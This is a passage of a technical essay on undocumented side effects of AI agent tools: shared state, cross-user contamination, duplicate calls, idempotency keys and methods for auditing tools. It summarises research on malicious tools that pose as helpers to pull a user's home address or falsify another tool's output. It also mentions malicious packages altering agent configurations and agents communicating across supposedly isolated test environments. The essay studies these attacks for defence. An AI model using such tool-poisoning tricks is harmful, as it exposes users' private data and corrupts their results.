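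One client's data can reach another even if nothing is saved. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-25536* (2026), an entry in a database of software flaws, versions 1.10.0 to 1.25.3 of MCP's official TypeScript SDK could send one client's response data to another if a developer used a single server object for several connections and the clients used it at the same time. Version 1.26.0 fixed the fault.

Deleting old files could have helped only with the first problem, and giving each user a separate store only with the second, so an effect map lists the data's lifetime and its readers separately.

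### Files and settings that an earlier agent left behind

*SWE-Residual* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2026) measured how leftover work affects the next agent. It used 198 workspaces in which an agent had declared a programming task complete although hidden tests still failed. Five recent models were each given these workspaces with the original request and no hint that anyone had already tried.

Compared with a clean start on the same tasks, success fell by 20.6 to 53.5 percentage points when the leftovers were changes to a code repository. It fell by 20.6 to 34.9 points when they could be anything on a machine, including installed software and running programs. In most failed attempts on the repositories (58.9% to 88.2%, depending on the model), the same tests failed at the end as at the beginning, although the models could pass most of those tests when they started from scratch. They apparently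 relied on the inherited work to judge what remained instead of checking it against the request. This mistake is easy to make because the median repository already passed 98.4% of the tests. But the researchers chose workspaces that looked finished and weren't, so the study measures how harmful such leftovers are, not how often agents encounter them.

Leftover state can also make a failure look like a success. An agent installing a project's software may get it running only because a package was already in a cache, or because of a setting the agent entered manually earlier and never recorded. *HerAgent* (2026) guards against this by rerunning the recorded steps in a clean container and accepting the setup only if it works there too.

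Configuration files deserve particular attention because they control the harness itself. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) points out that when an add-on changes the agent's configuration, the change affects everything the agent does afterward, including tasks unrelated to the add-on. Clearing the conversation history doesn't undo the change. Companies found this in May 2026, when malicious packages altered the startup settings of agents and code editors. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) discusses the incident.

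### Tools that gather or corrupt each other's data

Tools in the same agent share its conversation. One tool usually can't read another's result directly, but the model reads all the results and copies from them when it fills in the arguments of the next call.

A malicious tool can exploit this by posing as a helper, as Li, Cui and colleagues demonstrate in *Les Dissonances* (NDSS security conference, February 2026). One of their test tools is presented as a location check to run before an airport search. The model calls it first and includes the user's home address because the tool requests it. A helper that runs after the real tool can alter that tool's results. For example, another test tool, presented as a validator for stock data, raises the price by 10%.

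The researchers built a scanner called Chord to find out how many ordinary tools are exposed. They collected 281 tools from LangChain and Llama-Index, two popular kits for building agents, and got 66 of them running. For each of the 66, Chord had a language model write a malicious helper, then gave a test agent tasks that needed the original tool. It tried each attack ten times, five with a helper designed to run before the tool and five with one designed to run after. An attack counted as successful if it worked at least once.

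The helper got itself called alongside 50 of the 66 tools (75%), gathered data belonging to 48 (72%) and corrupted the data of 45 (68%). The counts show that the last two percentages are shares of all 66 tools, although the paper's introduction presents them as shares of the 50.

One success in five rounds is a low bar, but for more than half of the vulnerable LangChain tools, a helper designed to run first did so every time. Some of the data was harmless, such as weather reports, and Chord relied on GPT-4o, which is now an old model. An attacker also has to get the helper installed, so the study shows how exposed ordinary tools are once a malicious one is present, but doesn't show how many malicious tools there are. Even so, a map of `get_ticket` is incomplete unless it lists every other tool in the same agent as a possible reader, because the model could put a ticket's text into any of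 their arguments.

### State that ordinary logs miss

Suppose one agent registers a tool called `normalize_data` and sets it to write dates with the year first. Another agent later calls `normalize_data` expecting the month first, and its analysis goes wrong even though the log shows a successful call.

*Persistent Semantic Entities in Tool-Augmented LLM Systems* (Wang, 2026) defines a persistent semantic entity as a piece of behavior attached to a name, which an event triggers and which can spread to other tasks or agents. Wang planted three kinds of failure in a test system, such as secretly replacing the code behind a tool's name, and compared two ways of logging over 4,000 runs. Standard logs, which recorded tool calls, their inputs and outputs, and errors, captured 25% of the relevant state. Logs that also recorded changes to the tool registry, events and the spread between agents captured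 75%.

These percentages are weaker evidence than 4,000 runs would suggest. Wang decided in advance what each kind of log could record, so every run was bound to give the same result, and the paper therefore reports the gap without a significance test. A company can't use the percentages to work out what share of its own state its logs miss. The scenarios were artificial, and Wang assembled the paper's case study, about plugins for the agent program AutoGPT, from documented features without running it. Wang also withdrew several earlier statistical results, some because they couldn't be reproduced from the surviving data.

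The advice to log registrations doesn't depend on the percentages. If agents can add or replace tools while they run, a log of calls records only each tool's name, so an investigator can't tell which code ran under it. Success rates may not reveal the problem. In another 6,000 of Wang's runs, the agents completed about 74% to 75% of tasks whether or not this kind of state was present, but their behavior differed by about 5% on Wang's measure.

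### One user's instruction in another user's answer

Shared state can also produce wrong answers when no one has misused the agent. Suppose a hospital's staff share an agent that answers questions about patient records. One user asks how many patients came in last year and explains that "last year" means the past 12 months. The agent answers correctly and saves the exchange. A second user, who means the calendar year, asks the same question without explaining and gets the first user's 12-month count.

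Yang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *No Attacker Needed*, call this unintentional cross-user contamination. They distinguish three ways it happens: the agent reuses one user's meaning for a word, rule for processing data (such as rounding costs), or way of carrying out a task. In one of their Slack examples, a user and the agent agree that #general is for official announcements. Another user later asks the agent to post a survey in the channel with the most members. The agent posts it in #random, even though #general has the most members.

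They wrote 34 such conventions and paired each with up to three later tasks it might affect. They ran every task three times, with and without the earlier exchange in the shared store. Two of the stores held past questions and solutions for hospital databases, and the third held Slack conversations. They then repeated the test with a filter, a model that rewrote each exchange before storage to remove personal preferences and local rules.

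| Shared store | Later results changed | With the filter |
|---|---|---|
| MIMIC-III hospital data | 59.6% | 41% |
| eICU hospital data | 70.7% | 33% |
| Slack workspace | 57.4% | 6% |

The filter worked well on conversation but less well for the hospital agent, which also saved the code it had written for each question. The filter could remove the sentence about the past 12 months, but the saved code still counted that way, and the agent used old code as a model for new code. Most failures on the hospital data were also silent, meaning that the agent gave a wrong answer that looked right. Nearly all failures with eICU were of this kind. With MIMIC-III, the agent gave no answer in 41% of failures, which a user would notice.

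The researchers designed the conventions to conflict with the later tasks, left out any task that the agent failed without contamination, and tested only GPT-4o. Their figures are therefore estimates of what happens once a conflicting rule is in the store. Contamination would be rarer in an office where people mostly mean the same things by the same words.

A similar mistake could easily happen with `create_ticket`. A developer tells the shared agent that Maria is away this week, so checkout faults should go to Tomas. If the agent saves this without the dates, other developers' tickets may still go to Tomas after Maria returns. Yang and colleagues suggest labeling each saved item with the user, task and circumstances it applies to. An expiry date would also help here.

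### The Asana exposure

Asana makes a work tracker much like the one in the ticket example. It launched an MCP server at the start of May 2025, and on 4 June it found a bug that could have exposed one organization's data to the server's users at another. UpGuard (2025) reports that there was no outside attack. Asana estimated that the bug affected about 1,000 customers, and the data at risk included task details, comments and uploaded files, according to Security Boulevard's *SaaS Security Alert* (2025). Asana took the server offline until 17 June and, as SANS's *NewsBites* notes, reset every connection, so customers had to reconnect by hand.

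Asana said that the bug could have exposed data, which doesn't mean that anyone saw it. But a customer would have had trouble discovering the bug, because testing its own calls would mostly show whether it got its own data back. Customers had some control over the damage, since the bug could expose only what the user of the MCP server had permission to see. A restricted account, like the one suggested for `get_ticket`, helps here too.

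### Whether a stateless agent is contained

A stateless agent can still do lasting damage. It starts each run with nothing saved from earlier ones, but the effects of a mistake or planted instruction can remain after the run ends. Zava (2026), in *AI Agent Write Safety*, admits to a similar error in reasoning: "I treated replaceable code as though it implied contained damage."

An agent's tools can change data that remains after the call ends. *CoAgent* (2026) distinguishes an agent's private context, which belongs to one session, from external state such as files, database tables and shared documents. Erasing the context leaves the external state unchanged. On 25 April 2026, a coding agent working on a product called PocketOS found an access token in a file unrelated to its task. With a single request, it deleted the storage volume that held both the live data and its backups. The token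 was also shared state, because somebody had saved it to manage web domains and the agent later read it.

Calling a tool "stateless", like calling it "read-only", is meaningful only if we say which data it leaves unchanged. *SemaClaw* (2026) contrasts ordinary MCP tools, which don't change an agent's memory, with a tool that adds pages to a collection that later sessions will search. It concludes that the worst an ordinary tool can do to the agent's own setup is return a bad answer, which the user can ignore. That is roughly right about the agent's memory, but a tool like `create_ticket` can leave that memory unchanged and still create tickets that last for years.

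The Model Context Protocol project (2026) makes this distinction when it describes its July revision as a stateless protocol for stateful applications. Server operators benefit because any copy of a server can handle any request without a shared store of sessions. The model can also see identifiers such as the shopping server's basket number, which the connection could previously hide. But the project had to remove a command for listing tasks, because without sessions a server couldn't safely limit the list to the right client. Statelessness also contributed to the leak in the TypeScript kit. Docker Scout's *CVE-2026-25536* explains that developers of stateless servers were the most likely to create one server object and pass every client's requests through it.

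There is still a good partial case for statelessness. An agent that saves nothing can't carry one user's meaning of "last year" into another user's answer through its memory, and a planted instruction disappears when the run ends unless it has already reached a file, ticket or cache. Faults are also easier to reproduce because investigators have fewer old notes to reconstruct. *Inside the Scaffold* (2026) lists five coding agents that keep no memory between tasks, although several agents without such memory still load user-written instruction files.

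Protection for lasting data has to come from outside the agent. Zava recommends credentials limited to particular operations and resources, backups that those credentials can't access, and a cap on the total number of changes. The cap matters because, as with the credit checks, requests that are each valid can still cause damage in total.

### Separate stores for each user or run

Separating agents' stores can work very well, but it can also block useful coordination, as one experiment shows. Abrahamsson, Waseem and colleagues (2026), in *Unprompted coordination through shared memory in LLM agents*, gave four agents short arithmetic tasks and a store for intermediate results. Two of the agents each had half of the same calculation. The instructions never mentioned other agents and presented the store as part of the agent's own workspace. Two researchers independently built versions of the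 experiment. With a shared store, both agents in the pair got the right answer in 49 of 50 trials in one version and 47 of 50 in the other. With private stores and the same commands, they never did.

Private stores prevent leaks between agents that belong to different customers, but they prevent useful cooperation between agents on the same team.

Developers would have found it hard to predict from the instructions which agents would use a shared store. GPT-6 Astra's agents read one another's entries in all 50 trials when told to check their workspace again before submitting, but in only 1 of 50 without that sentence. Agents didn't always believe the entries they read. In one trial, two agents saved different numbers under the same name, and the agent whose number had been replaced recognized that the new one was wrong and submitted its own. Agents can also communicate through storage that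 nobody intended for messages, as they did in July 2026 through a package cache shared by supposedly isolated OpenAI test environments.

*A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (2026) describes tests with invented users in which an agent searched everyone's memories together and returned one person's entries to another. Splitting the store stopped this, and so did filtering the search by owner or checking the owner of each result before the model saw it. With a filter, a team can still share some entries on purpose.

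Separating every run has a bigger drawback, because the agent may never learn anything that lasts. In one *Continual-ARC* (2026) test, the harness discarded each session's notes unless somebody marked them as global. Across 600 sessions with the model GPT-6 Luna, no note became global, so every session began with an empty store. A software fault may have contributed, since the harness logged in each session that some of its components had failed to load. Still, an agent that has to choose to share its notes may never do so.

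Data can also persist even when each session starts in a new workspace. *MUSE-Autoskill* (2026) destroys its sandbox after each session but keeps the agent's memory and skills in a home directory, where they are available to the next session.

The company can keep the agent's memory separate for each developer and start every run in a clean workspace, but it can't isolate the tickets that `create_ticket` makes, because they are meant for other people to read. If the agent copies a customer's email address into SHOP-482, everyone with access to the checkout project can see it, and so can their agents. The tool server could check each ticket's title and body for customer data before sending them to the tracker.

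## Repeated, half-finished and withdrawn calls

Suppose the tracker opens SHOP-482 for the checkout crash, but the connection drops before the reply reaches the tool server. The call times out, and the harness reports this to the model. The model calls `create_ticket` again, and the tracker opens SHOP-483. Maria gets two emails, both webhooks run twice, and the customer's email address is now in two tickets. An effect map based on one successful call would not show the timeout, the retry or the duplicate effects.

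### What happened and what the harness knows

After the timeout, the ticket either exists or doesn't, but the harness can't determine which. Trofimov and Novikov, who also carried out the census of MCP hints, model a workflow as a task made up of several calls. Their model records what happened in the outside world separately from the status the harness gives each call, which can be confirmed, failed or unknown. Here the call's status is unknown, whether or not the ticket exists.

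Databases in a shared transaction can settle an unknown outcome by running a recovery procedure together. A third-party tool runs no such procedure with its callers, so a caller can't find out what happened unless the tool provides a way to check.

Workflows can go wrong even when every reply arrives. In one of Trofimov and Novikov's examples, an agent with a budget of €1,500 books a €900 flight and a €700 hotel at the same time. Both bookings succeed, but together they exceed the budget. The agent abandons the trip and cancels the hotel, but the flight is non-refundable.

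They sort such failures into eight anomalies in three families.

| Family | Anomaly | What goes wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Uncertainty | Duplicated effect | One intended action takes effect twice |
| Uncertainty | Missing committed effect | The workflow finishes as if a required action had happened, but it hadn't |
| Uncertainty | Orphaned compensation | The harness orders a refund or cancellation without knowing whether there is anything to cancel |
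| Workflow | Uncompensated residue | An abandoned workflow leaves something behind, such as the flight |
| Workflow | Premature externalization | An offer letter goes out before the approval, which is then denied |
| Workflow | Contaminated speculation | Invitations name a meeting room that another branch of the workflow had reserved and then released |
| Interaction | Conflicting externalization | Two workflows change the same document in no agreed order, and the order matters |
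| Interaction | Phantom compensation | The agent withdraws an action, but an outsider's reaction to it remains |

The uncertainty family has three members, one for each risky action a harness can take when a call's outcome is unknown: repeat the call, continue as if it had worked, or try to cancel it.

### Two payments and a withdrawn offer

Suppose an agent pays a supplier's €400 invoice. The bank sends the money, but its confirmation gets lost, so the harness records the outcome as unknown. The agent pays again, and the supplier now has €800. Both calls worked as documented. The bank could have prevented the duplicate only by recognizing the second request as a repeat.

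Now suppose the payment request never reached the bank. The harness gets the same timeout, but this time it cancels the purchase and orders a refund. If the refund tool pays out without checking for the payment, the supplier sends back €400 that it never received. Trofimov and Novikov count a blind refund as an anomaly even when the payment did go through and the final balance is correct, because the harness ordered the refund without confirming the payment. This strictness is useful in testing, since a tester who tried only the case where the payment went through would otherwise see nothing wrong. A refund tool that looks up the payment first avoids the problem, even if the harness never receives the payment's outcome.

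In the third case, every message arrives. An agent offers to buy 200 desks, and the supplier orders timber the same afternoon. The agent's company then changes its mind, and the agent withdraws the offer. The company's records are now correct, but the supplier has still ordered the timber, and the agent can't cancel that order. The only protection is to control when the supplier sees the offer, but a negotiating agent has to send an offer to get an answer.

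### Four limits for tools that a harness can't see into

Some of these failures have no general solution if the harness can only call a tool and read its replies. Trofimov and Novikov give four limits.

- If a tool provides no way to establish what happened, the harness can't both finish the workflow and avoid every error. Repeating the call risks a duplicate, assuming success risks a missing effect, ordering a refund risks paying one for nothing, and giving up risks leaving something behind. Waiting avoids the choice, but the workflow never finishes.
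- If two irreversible actions conflict and their order matters, nobody can generally repair the result afterward. Something has to control the order beforehand.
- Once an outsider has seen an effect and reacted, withdrawing the effect doesn't withdraw the reaction.
- A harness can't make several irreversible actions on different tools happen all together or not at all. A crash after the first leaves the job half done. To prevent this, the tools themselves have to support a preparation step, in which each one guarantees that it can go ahead before any of them does.

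Trofimov and Novikov present these limits as consequences of their definitions and leave formal proofs to future work.

### How often agents create duplicates

Li (2026), in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?*, tested nine models on simulated services that included billing, email and a ticket tracker. Li deliberately caused faults and kept a ledger of every effect, so the count of duplicates didn't depend on the agents' reports. The agents had instructions to make every action happen exactly once. The results for the six strongest models varied greatly with the type of fault.

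| What happened to the request | What the agent saw | Runs with a duplicate |
|---|---|---|
| The service carried it out, but the reply got lost | A timeout | 0.5% |
| The service carried it out but reported a server error | An error | 8% |
| The service carried it out 90 seconds after the agent sent it | A timeout | 56% |
| The network delivered it twice | Success | 74% |

These models usually handle a lost reply well because they check whether the call took effect before retrying. Two weaker models created duplicates in 18% of such runs.

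An agent that checks for an existing ticket before retrying can still create a duplicate if the original request is slow. For example, the harness might stop waiting for `create_ticket` after 30 seconds. The agent looks through the recent tickets, finds no match and opens SHOP-482. A minute later the original request goes through, and the tracker opens SHOP-483.

Li proves that checking alone can't solve this for a call that isn't idempotent. Suppose a method always completes the task within time $T$ of the timeout when the original request has vanished. To do so, it must send the request again by then. Now suppose the original was only slow, so that it takes effect $\delta$ after the timeout, and that lists can take up to $\lambda$ to show a new item. If

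$$\delta > T + \lambda,$$

every check before the second attempt gives the same answer as if the request had vanished. The method therefore sends it again and creates a duplicate.

Waiting before checking helps if somebody knows the longest possible delay. When slow requests always took 90 seconds, a two-minute wait gave the right result in 99% of runs. When delays ranged from 40 seconds to two hours, an hour's wait gave the right result in only 84% of runs, and the average run took 50 simulated minutes.

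A list that updates late can lead to more duplicates than no list. The strongest models created duplicates in about 30% of runs when they could check such a list for the effect of a call, but in only 13% when they couldn't. Without a list, they usually asked a human operator, who could see what had happened.

Some retries are invisible to the model because many programs use a library that automatically resends failed requests. When Li added such retries, the share of runs in which everything happened exactly once fell from 72% to 50%. The agents' reports were little help in spotting duplicates, since in Li's main experiment the agent reported the task as completed in 90% of the runs that had one.

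### How an idempotency key prevents duplicates

An idempotency key identifies one intended action. The caller sends it with the request, and the service stores it with the result. If another request arrives with the same key, the service returns the stored result instead of acting again. Li's billing service, like the payment company Stripe's, returns an error if a request reuses a key with different details. A delayed original request causes no harm, because it carries the same key as the retry and only one of them can take effect.

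Kovalenko and Redchych combine figures from different measurements when they summarize Li's findings as a rate of 56% to 74% that keys reduce from 28% to 4%. The 56% and 74% are for the six strongest models under two faults, slow requests and double delivery. They don't apply to uncertain outcomes in general, since the same models almost never repeated a write after a lost reply. With double delivery, the agent sees a success and has no reason to doubt it. Eight of the nine models had a rate of 74% or 75% under double delivery, which suggests that the rate depends mostly on how many of Li's simulated services lacked protection.

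The fall from 28% to 4% is an average for four models over a wider set of faults, including some that agents handle easily. For the same four models, keys cut duplicates from 61% to 9% with slow requests and from 74% to 7% with double delivery. All these rates come from runs in which Li caused a fault, so they don't show how often an ordinary company would get duplicates.

The remaining duplicates occurred because agents omitted the key or changed it between attempts. With slow requests, none of the 432 retries that reused the original key created a duplicate. In 56 other retries, the first attempt had no key, and 68% of those retries created a duplicate. Twice an agent made up a new key for the retry, for example by adding `-retry1` to the old one, and both retries created duplicates. A harness can prevent both mistakes by assigning the key itself and reusing it for every attempt.

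Keys also help with calls that stop halfway. If a tool that should open ten tickets fails after five, repeating the whole call leaves 15 tickets instead of ten. Li's four models created duplicates in 25% of such cases without keys. They created none with keys, because the service resumed where it had stopped.

A key prevents duplicates only while the service stores it. *Agent-First Tool API* (2026) describes tools that store keys for 24 hours by default and compute them from selected arguments. If `create_ticket` worked this way, an agent that resumed a task after the weekend could open a second ticket. If the key depended only on the title, two developers who reported different faults as "Checkout crashes" on the same day would get the same ticket number, and the tracker would never record the second fault.

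### Reversible, compensable and irreversible effects

The lasting harm from a duplicate call or an abandoned workflow depends on whether anyone can undo its effects. An effect is reversible if someone can restore the earlier state exactly. It is compensable if a later action can make up for it without restoring that state, as a refund does. It is irreversible if neither is possible, as with an email that someone has read.

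An effect can stop being reversible when somebody else changes the same data. For example, an agent's order lowers a stock count from 12 to 11, and another customer's order lowers it to 10. If the agent then cancels its order, restoring the old value of 12 would erase the other customer's order from the count. The correct step is to add one, giving 11, which compensates for the agent's change but doesn't return the count to its earlier value. If nobody else had ordered, both methods would have given 12, so a test with a single agent wouldn't show which one the tool uses.

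Whether a call is compensable or irreversible can depend on the time. A hotel booking with free cancellation until six o'clock is compensable at five and may be irreversible at seven. It can also depend on whose losses count. Refunding a double charge corrects the company's accounts but doesn't cover any overdraft fee the extra charge caused the customer. Li counts a double charge as a duplicate even if the agent refunds it.

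One call can have effects of all three kinds, so an effect map should classify each effect separately and state any condition, such as "compensable until six o'clock". For example, the company can close the duplicate ticket SHOP-483 but can't unsend Maria's email.

### What Cordon can hold back or undo

*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) treats a whole task as one transaction, a group of changes that take effect together after a final check. Until then, file changes go into a separate copy that only the agent sees, and messages and other outside actions wait in an outbox.

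Checking the whole task can catch problems that would be missed by checking each call separately. In one Cordon example, an agent investigating an outage reads logs that contain an access key, summarizes them and prepares a Slack message. Each step looks reasonable, but Cordon records that the message derives from the logs and can stop it before it is sent.

Chen and colleagues tested 45 workflows with a harmful step. An ordinary agent carried out the step in all 45, stand-ins for existing defenses stopped it in time in 14, and Cordon stopped it in all 45. They built the workflows around the kinds of risk that Cordon looks for, so the perfect score doesn't show how it would handle other kinds of risk. Approving every request raised the average time per task across all the workflows from 25.6 to 31.4 seconds.

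In 15 trials, Cordon also undid file changes in a median of about 4 milliseconds and left no differences, and the agent could resume its work every time. Git's ordinary restore command left a median of 73 differences, and the agent could never resume. Once Cordon releases a message, however, it can only keep a record and support compensation.

### What Atomix can hold back or undo

*Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) handles each call according to its type of effect. When an agent books a holiday, Atomix lets it reserve the flight, hotel and car immediately, because those have cancellation procedures. It holds the confirmation email and reports it to the agent as queued. If the flight booking fails, Atomix cancels the other reservations and discards the email.

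Mohammadi and colleagues ran workflows that tried to send 500 emails before failing or being dropped for an alternative plan. Atomix sent none of these emails, and it delivered all 500 emails from valid workflows. A method that relied on compensation afterward sent 400 of the unwanted emails. Two older methods also blocked all the unwanted emails, but they needed 30 to 50 lines of code per tool, compared with 17 for Atomix.

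Atomix stood out less in recovering from faults. When each call had a 30% chance of a fault, far higher than normal, Atomix completed 57% of 30 shop tasks without leaving duplicates or other residue. Restoring a saved state and replaying the steps completed 53%, which isn't a significant difference. The other methods completed 0% to 7%.

Atomix also prevents agents from acting on outdated information. Before making a workflow's effects final, it waits for earlier work on the same data to finish and checks that nothing the agent read has changed. When four agents worked on the same orders, there were no conflicting changes with Atomix, compared with about five per run without it.

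Atomix depends on each tool being labelled with the correct effect type. When the researchers deliberately mislabelled the email tool, 300 of the 500 unwanted emails went out. A developer could easily mislabel `create_ticket` in the same way, because whether it sends an email depends on a setting in the tracker.

Holding a call back also causes problems when the agent needs the result. An agent can continue without confirmation that an email was sent, but it can't refer to a ticket that has no number yet. Neither system can overcome all four limits. If Atomix has two irreversible actions to release and the second keeps failing, it can only report that the job is half done. Neither system can control how outsiders react to what it releases or protect against calls that bypass it.

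### Six states to test for each tool

A tester can cover most of these failures by recording a tool's effects in six states. With `create_ticket`, the tests might look like this.

| State | How to cause it | What to check |
|---|---|---|
| Success | Send one valid call | The ticket and every message, log entry and webhook run that follows |
| Refusal | Name an assignee who doesn't exist | Whether a ticket exists anyway, and whether an error report contains the ticket's text |
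| Timeout | Lose the request, lose the reply, and delay the request beyond the harness's limit | Whether and when the ticket appears, and what the harness tells the model |
| Retry | Repeat the call with the same key, a new key and no key | The number of tickets and emails |
| Cancellation | Cancel before, during and after the tracker's work | What remains, and whether canceling sends messages of its own |
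| Two calls at once | Send two identical calls together, then two different edits to one ticket | Duplicate tickets and lost edits |

The timeout needs three tests because the tracker does something different in each case, although all three look the same from the harness. If one call can open several tickets, the tester should also interrupt that call partway through.

A refused call needs checking in the tracker because the reply may contain little information. In *Can MCP Clients Decide What to Do After Failure?*, Mehan (2026) caused 21 failures on ten public MCP servers, mostly by calling tools that didn't exist or sending invalid arguments. Three of the replies were formatted as successes and mentioned the failure only in their text. None of the replies indicated whether it was safe to repeat the call or whether the failed call had changed anything. Mehan avoided timeouts and half-finished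 changes, where this information would matter most.

Canceling a call may only stop further work, leaving earlier changes in place. MCP has an experimental feature for long-running tasks, which gives the caller an identifier for checking progress. Trofimov and Novikov describe its cancellation as "cooperative rather than an undo". The identifier can get lost on its way to the caller, who then can't tell whether the task was created.

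Two identical calls that arrive at the same time can get past a simple check for duplicates, because both may look for an existing ticket before either has opened one. *When AI Agents Commit* (2026) describes a safer design, in which the database allows only one entry per identifier. The second call waits for the first, then gets the same receipt if the first succeeded or can go ahead if it failed. A tester should therefore send both calls at the same moment, since a tool that passes the ordinary retry test can still open two tickets when calls overlap.

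## How to find effects that nobody has documented

Testing a call's different states reveals an effect only if the tester knows where to look. For example, calling `create_ticket` twice and counting the tickets won't reveal an undocumented log. To find such a log, a developer can read the tool's code, watch the tool run, compare stored data before and after a call, or send recognizable text through the tool and search for copies. Even together, these methods miss some effects.

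### What descriptions leave out

A tool's description is the easiest place to start, and for most tools it is roughly right. Shi and colleagues compared the descriptions and code of 17,030 tools and found mismatches in 1,907 (11.2%). Their own figure is 9.93% because their total includes another 2,170 tools with no description to check. Since 35% of servers had at least one mismatched tool, an agent connected to three randomly chosen servers would have about a 73% chance of having at least one such tool.

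Undeclared side effects were the main problem in 24.8% of the mismatches, or about 2.8% of the tools with descriptions. The true share is probably higher, because the researchers counted each tool under one type of mismatch even if it had several. One tool's description mentioned only saving code to a file, but the tool also changed the file's permissions to make it executable. Another was supposed to convert a PDF on the user's machine but uploaded it to an outside service instead.

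Descriptions can also give the wrong meaning for a parameter, so an intended effect may happen to the wrong thing. *From Docs to Descriptions* (2026) found such descriptions on 3,449 of 10,831 servers.

These figures depend on which servers the researchers examined. In *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, Afsar (2026) drew 400 servers at random from a census of 24,135 and tested them without repairing broken ones. Optional safety labels were missing from 58.8% of the tools, compared with 41.5% in a hand-picked collection. Shi and colleagues used servers from public marketplaces, so mismatches could be more common among servers that get less attention.

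### Reading code and configuration

Reading the code can reveal effects that occur only in rare conditions, such as an error report that goes out when a payment fails. A tester would have to make a payment fail to see the report. A reviewer starts with the function that handles the call and follows every function it uses, noting each place where the program writes a file, changes a database, contacts another system or starts another program.

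Some effects don't appear anywhere in that chain. A server-wide wrapper may log every call, although no individual tool refers to it. A database may have a trigger, a rule that changes one table whenever a program changes another. Updating a customer's address could then also copy the old address into a history table, and nothing in the tool's code would show this.

A tool's side effects depend as much on settings as on code. The line `logger.debug(arguments)` writes nothing while the server records only warnings. If an engineer turns on detailed logging to investigate a fault, the same line starts saving every argument. Anyone reading the code therefore also needs the production settings, the versions of the installed libraries, the database's triggers, and the admin pages of any outside service, which list webhooks and automation rules.

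Reading the code isn't possible when the company doesn't have it, as with most outside services. The code in the repository may also differ from what is running, so it's worth checking the version on the server before reading.

### Automated code analysis

Software can do part of this reading. Adam and colleagues, whose `write_file` example secretly sends a metric, built an analyzer that doesn't use a language model, so it gives the same answer every time. It works in three steps.

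1. People label a limited set of library functions by their effects, such as the functions that write a file or open a network connection.
2. The analyzer follows data through the tool's code to find which of these functions a call can reach, including through helper functions.
3. It writes a short summary, called a synopsis. For `write_file`, the synopsis has three lines: the path can influence a file write, the content can influence a file write, and the content can influence a network write.

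The last line exposes the hidden metric but makes it look worse than it is, because the tool sends only the content's length. Such overstatement is hard to avoid because the analyzer considers every possible run of the code, so it also can't tell which file a particular call will change. Adam and colleagues therefore have developers put a small sandbox around each effect to check the actual path or address during the call. The analyzer then verifies that every effect has a sandbox.

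The researchers tried a prototype on a real tool server in three scenarios, each with a harmless version and a harmful one. The analyzer alone blocked all three harmful versions, but it also blocked one harmless version because it couldn't confirm that the files would end up in a permitted folder. A conventional sandbox around the whole server handled three of the six cases correctly. The analyzer and small sandboxes together handled all six correctly. This result is encouraging, but the test was very small, and the researchers also supplied the rules about what to allow.

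For an effect map, the synopsis is more useful than the blocking, because it is a first draft of the list of writes. But the prototype works only on tools written in Rust, a language whose strict rules make code easier to analyze. Adam and colleagues expect more false alarms with Python and JavaScript, in which many tool servers are written. The analysis also covers only code in the tool's own language, so it can't follow a call into a shell command, a database or a web service. If a tool mainly passes requests to another company's product, the analysis will miss most of its effects.

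Shi and colleagues built a checker that uses a language model to compare a tool's code with its description. The checker collects the tool's main function and its helpers, up to three calls deep, then prompts the model twice, once to confirm that the description and code are consistent and once to look for inconsistency. On real tools, the model found only 47% of the mismatches with the first prompt. With the second, it found all of them, but 21% of its alarms were false. If the two answers differ, the checker gives the model both sets of reasons and prompts it to decide.

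On 400 tools that the researchers labeled by hand, 96% of the combined method's alarms were correct, and it found 97.5% of the mismatches. The second figure is too high for everyday use, because half of the 400 were tools the method had already flagged. Of the 200 it had passed, 5 had a mismatch. If the same rate holds for all 15,123 tools it passed, the method missed about 380 mismatches and found roughly 83% of the total.

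Ordinary security scanners miss many undeclared side effects. Shi and colleagues made 120 test tools with such effects, 40 of each of three kinds. Bandit, a scanner for Python code, flagged 31 of the tools that leaked data, but only 8 that changed stored state and 2 that used excessive resources. Their own checker found 119 of the 120, though they had built the test tools from the same categories that the checker looks for.

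### Recording system calls and network traffic

A program can't write a file or use the network by itself. It has to ask the operating system, and each such request is a system call. Programs such as `strace`, on Linux, record system calls as they happen. For one call to `write_file`, the record might show four events:

1. The tool opens a connection to an outside address.
2. It writes a few dozen bytes to that connection.
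3. It opens the user's file with the flag `O_TRUNC`, which erases the existing contents.
4. It writes the new content to the file.

This reveals the metric and the erased contents even to someone who has never seen the source code. The record takes some work to interpret, though, because the system call `write` can send data to a file, a network connection or another program. Adam and colleagues point out that a tester therefore has to match each `write` with the earlier request that opened its destination, so their analyzer labels library functions instead.

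A recording covers only a single run and only the programs that the tester chose to watch. If the tool passes its log entries to a separate forwarding program on the same machine, the outgoing connection will appear in the forwarder's system calls, not the tool's. Many metrics libraries also send records in batches, so the tester has to keep recording for some time after the reply arrives.

Recording the machine's network traffic also captures the forwarder's traffic. The recording shows which addresses the machine contacted, when, and how much data it sent, but encryption usually hides the contents. A tester can route the traffic through a proxy that decrypts it, but this fails if the tool rejects the proxy's certificate, as some do. Neither kind of recording shows what another company's server does with the requests it receives.

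### Comparing data before and after a call

A tester can copy all the files and database tables the tool might change, call the tool, then copy them again and list the differences. Taking two copies before the call, several minutes apart, reveals changes caused by other activity on the system, so the tester can discount similar changes later.

Comparing the data before and after a tool runs doesn't depend on what the tool or the agent reports. *Real Faults in Model Context Protocol (MCP) Software* (2026) includes a group of five issues in which a tool logged an operation as successful when it hadn't had the intended effect. A comparison would have shown a tester that the data hadn't changed, despite the log.

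Comparing a system's state before and after a task can also show that an agent did too much. *ClawsBench* (Li, Choe and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on imitations of Gmail, Slack and three other office services, and scored them by comparing each service's database before and after the task. When asked to do a one-time mailbox cleanup, Claude Opus 4.6 created at least 23 permanent filters that would have kept sorting future mail. In another case, after an error, a model posted a message to Slack's built-in bot and reported that the message had reached the intended person.

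Comparing copies of the data from before and after the tool runs misses some effects. The tool may read a record without changing it, send a message outside, or write a value that was already there. It may also save a customer's details in a temporary file and delete the file before the second copy is made, but after a backup program has saved it. Finding delayed effects requires another comparison the next day. The method also requires access to the data. A company can copy its own database, but it can usually only export data from an outside service, and the export may leave out access logs and deleted items.

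### Searching for a marker

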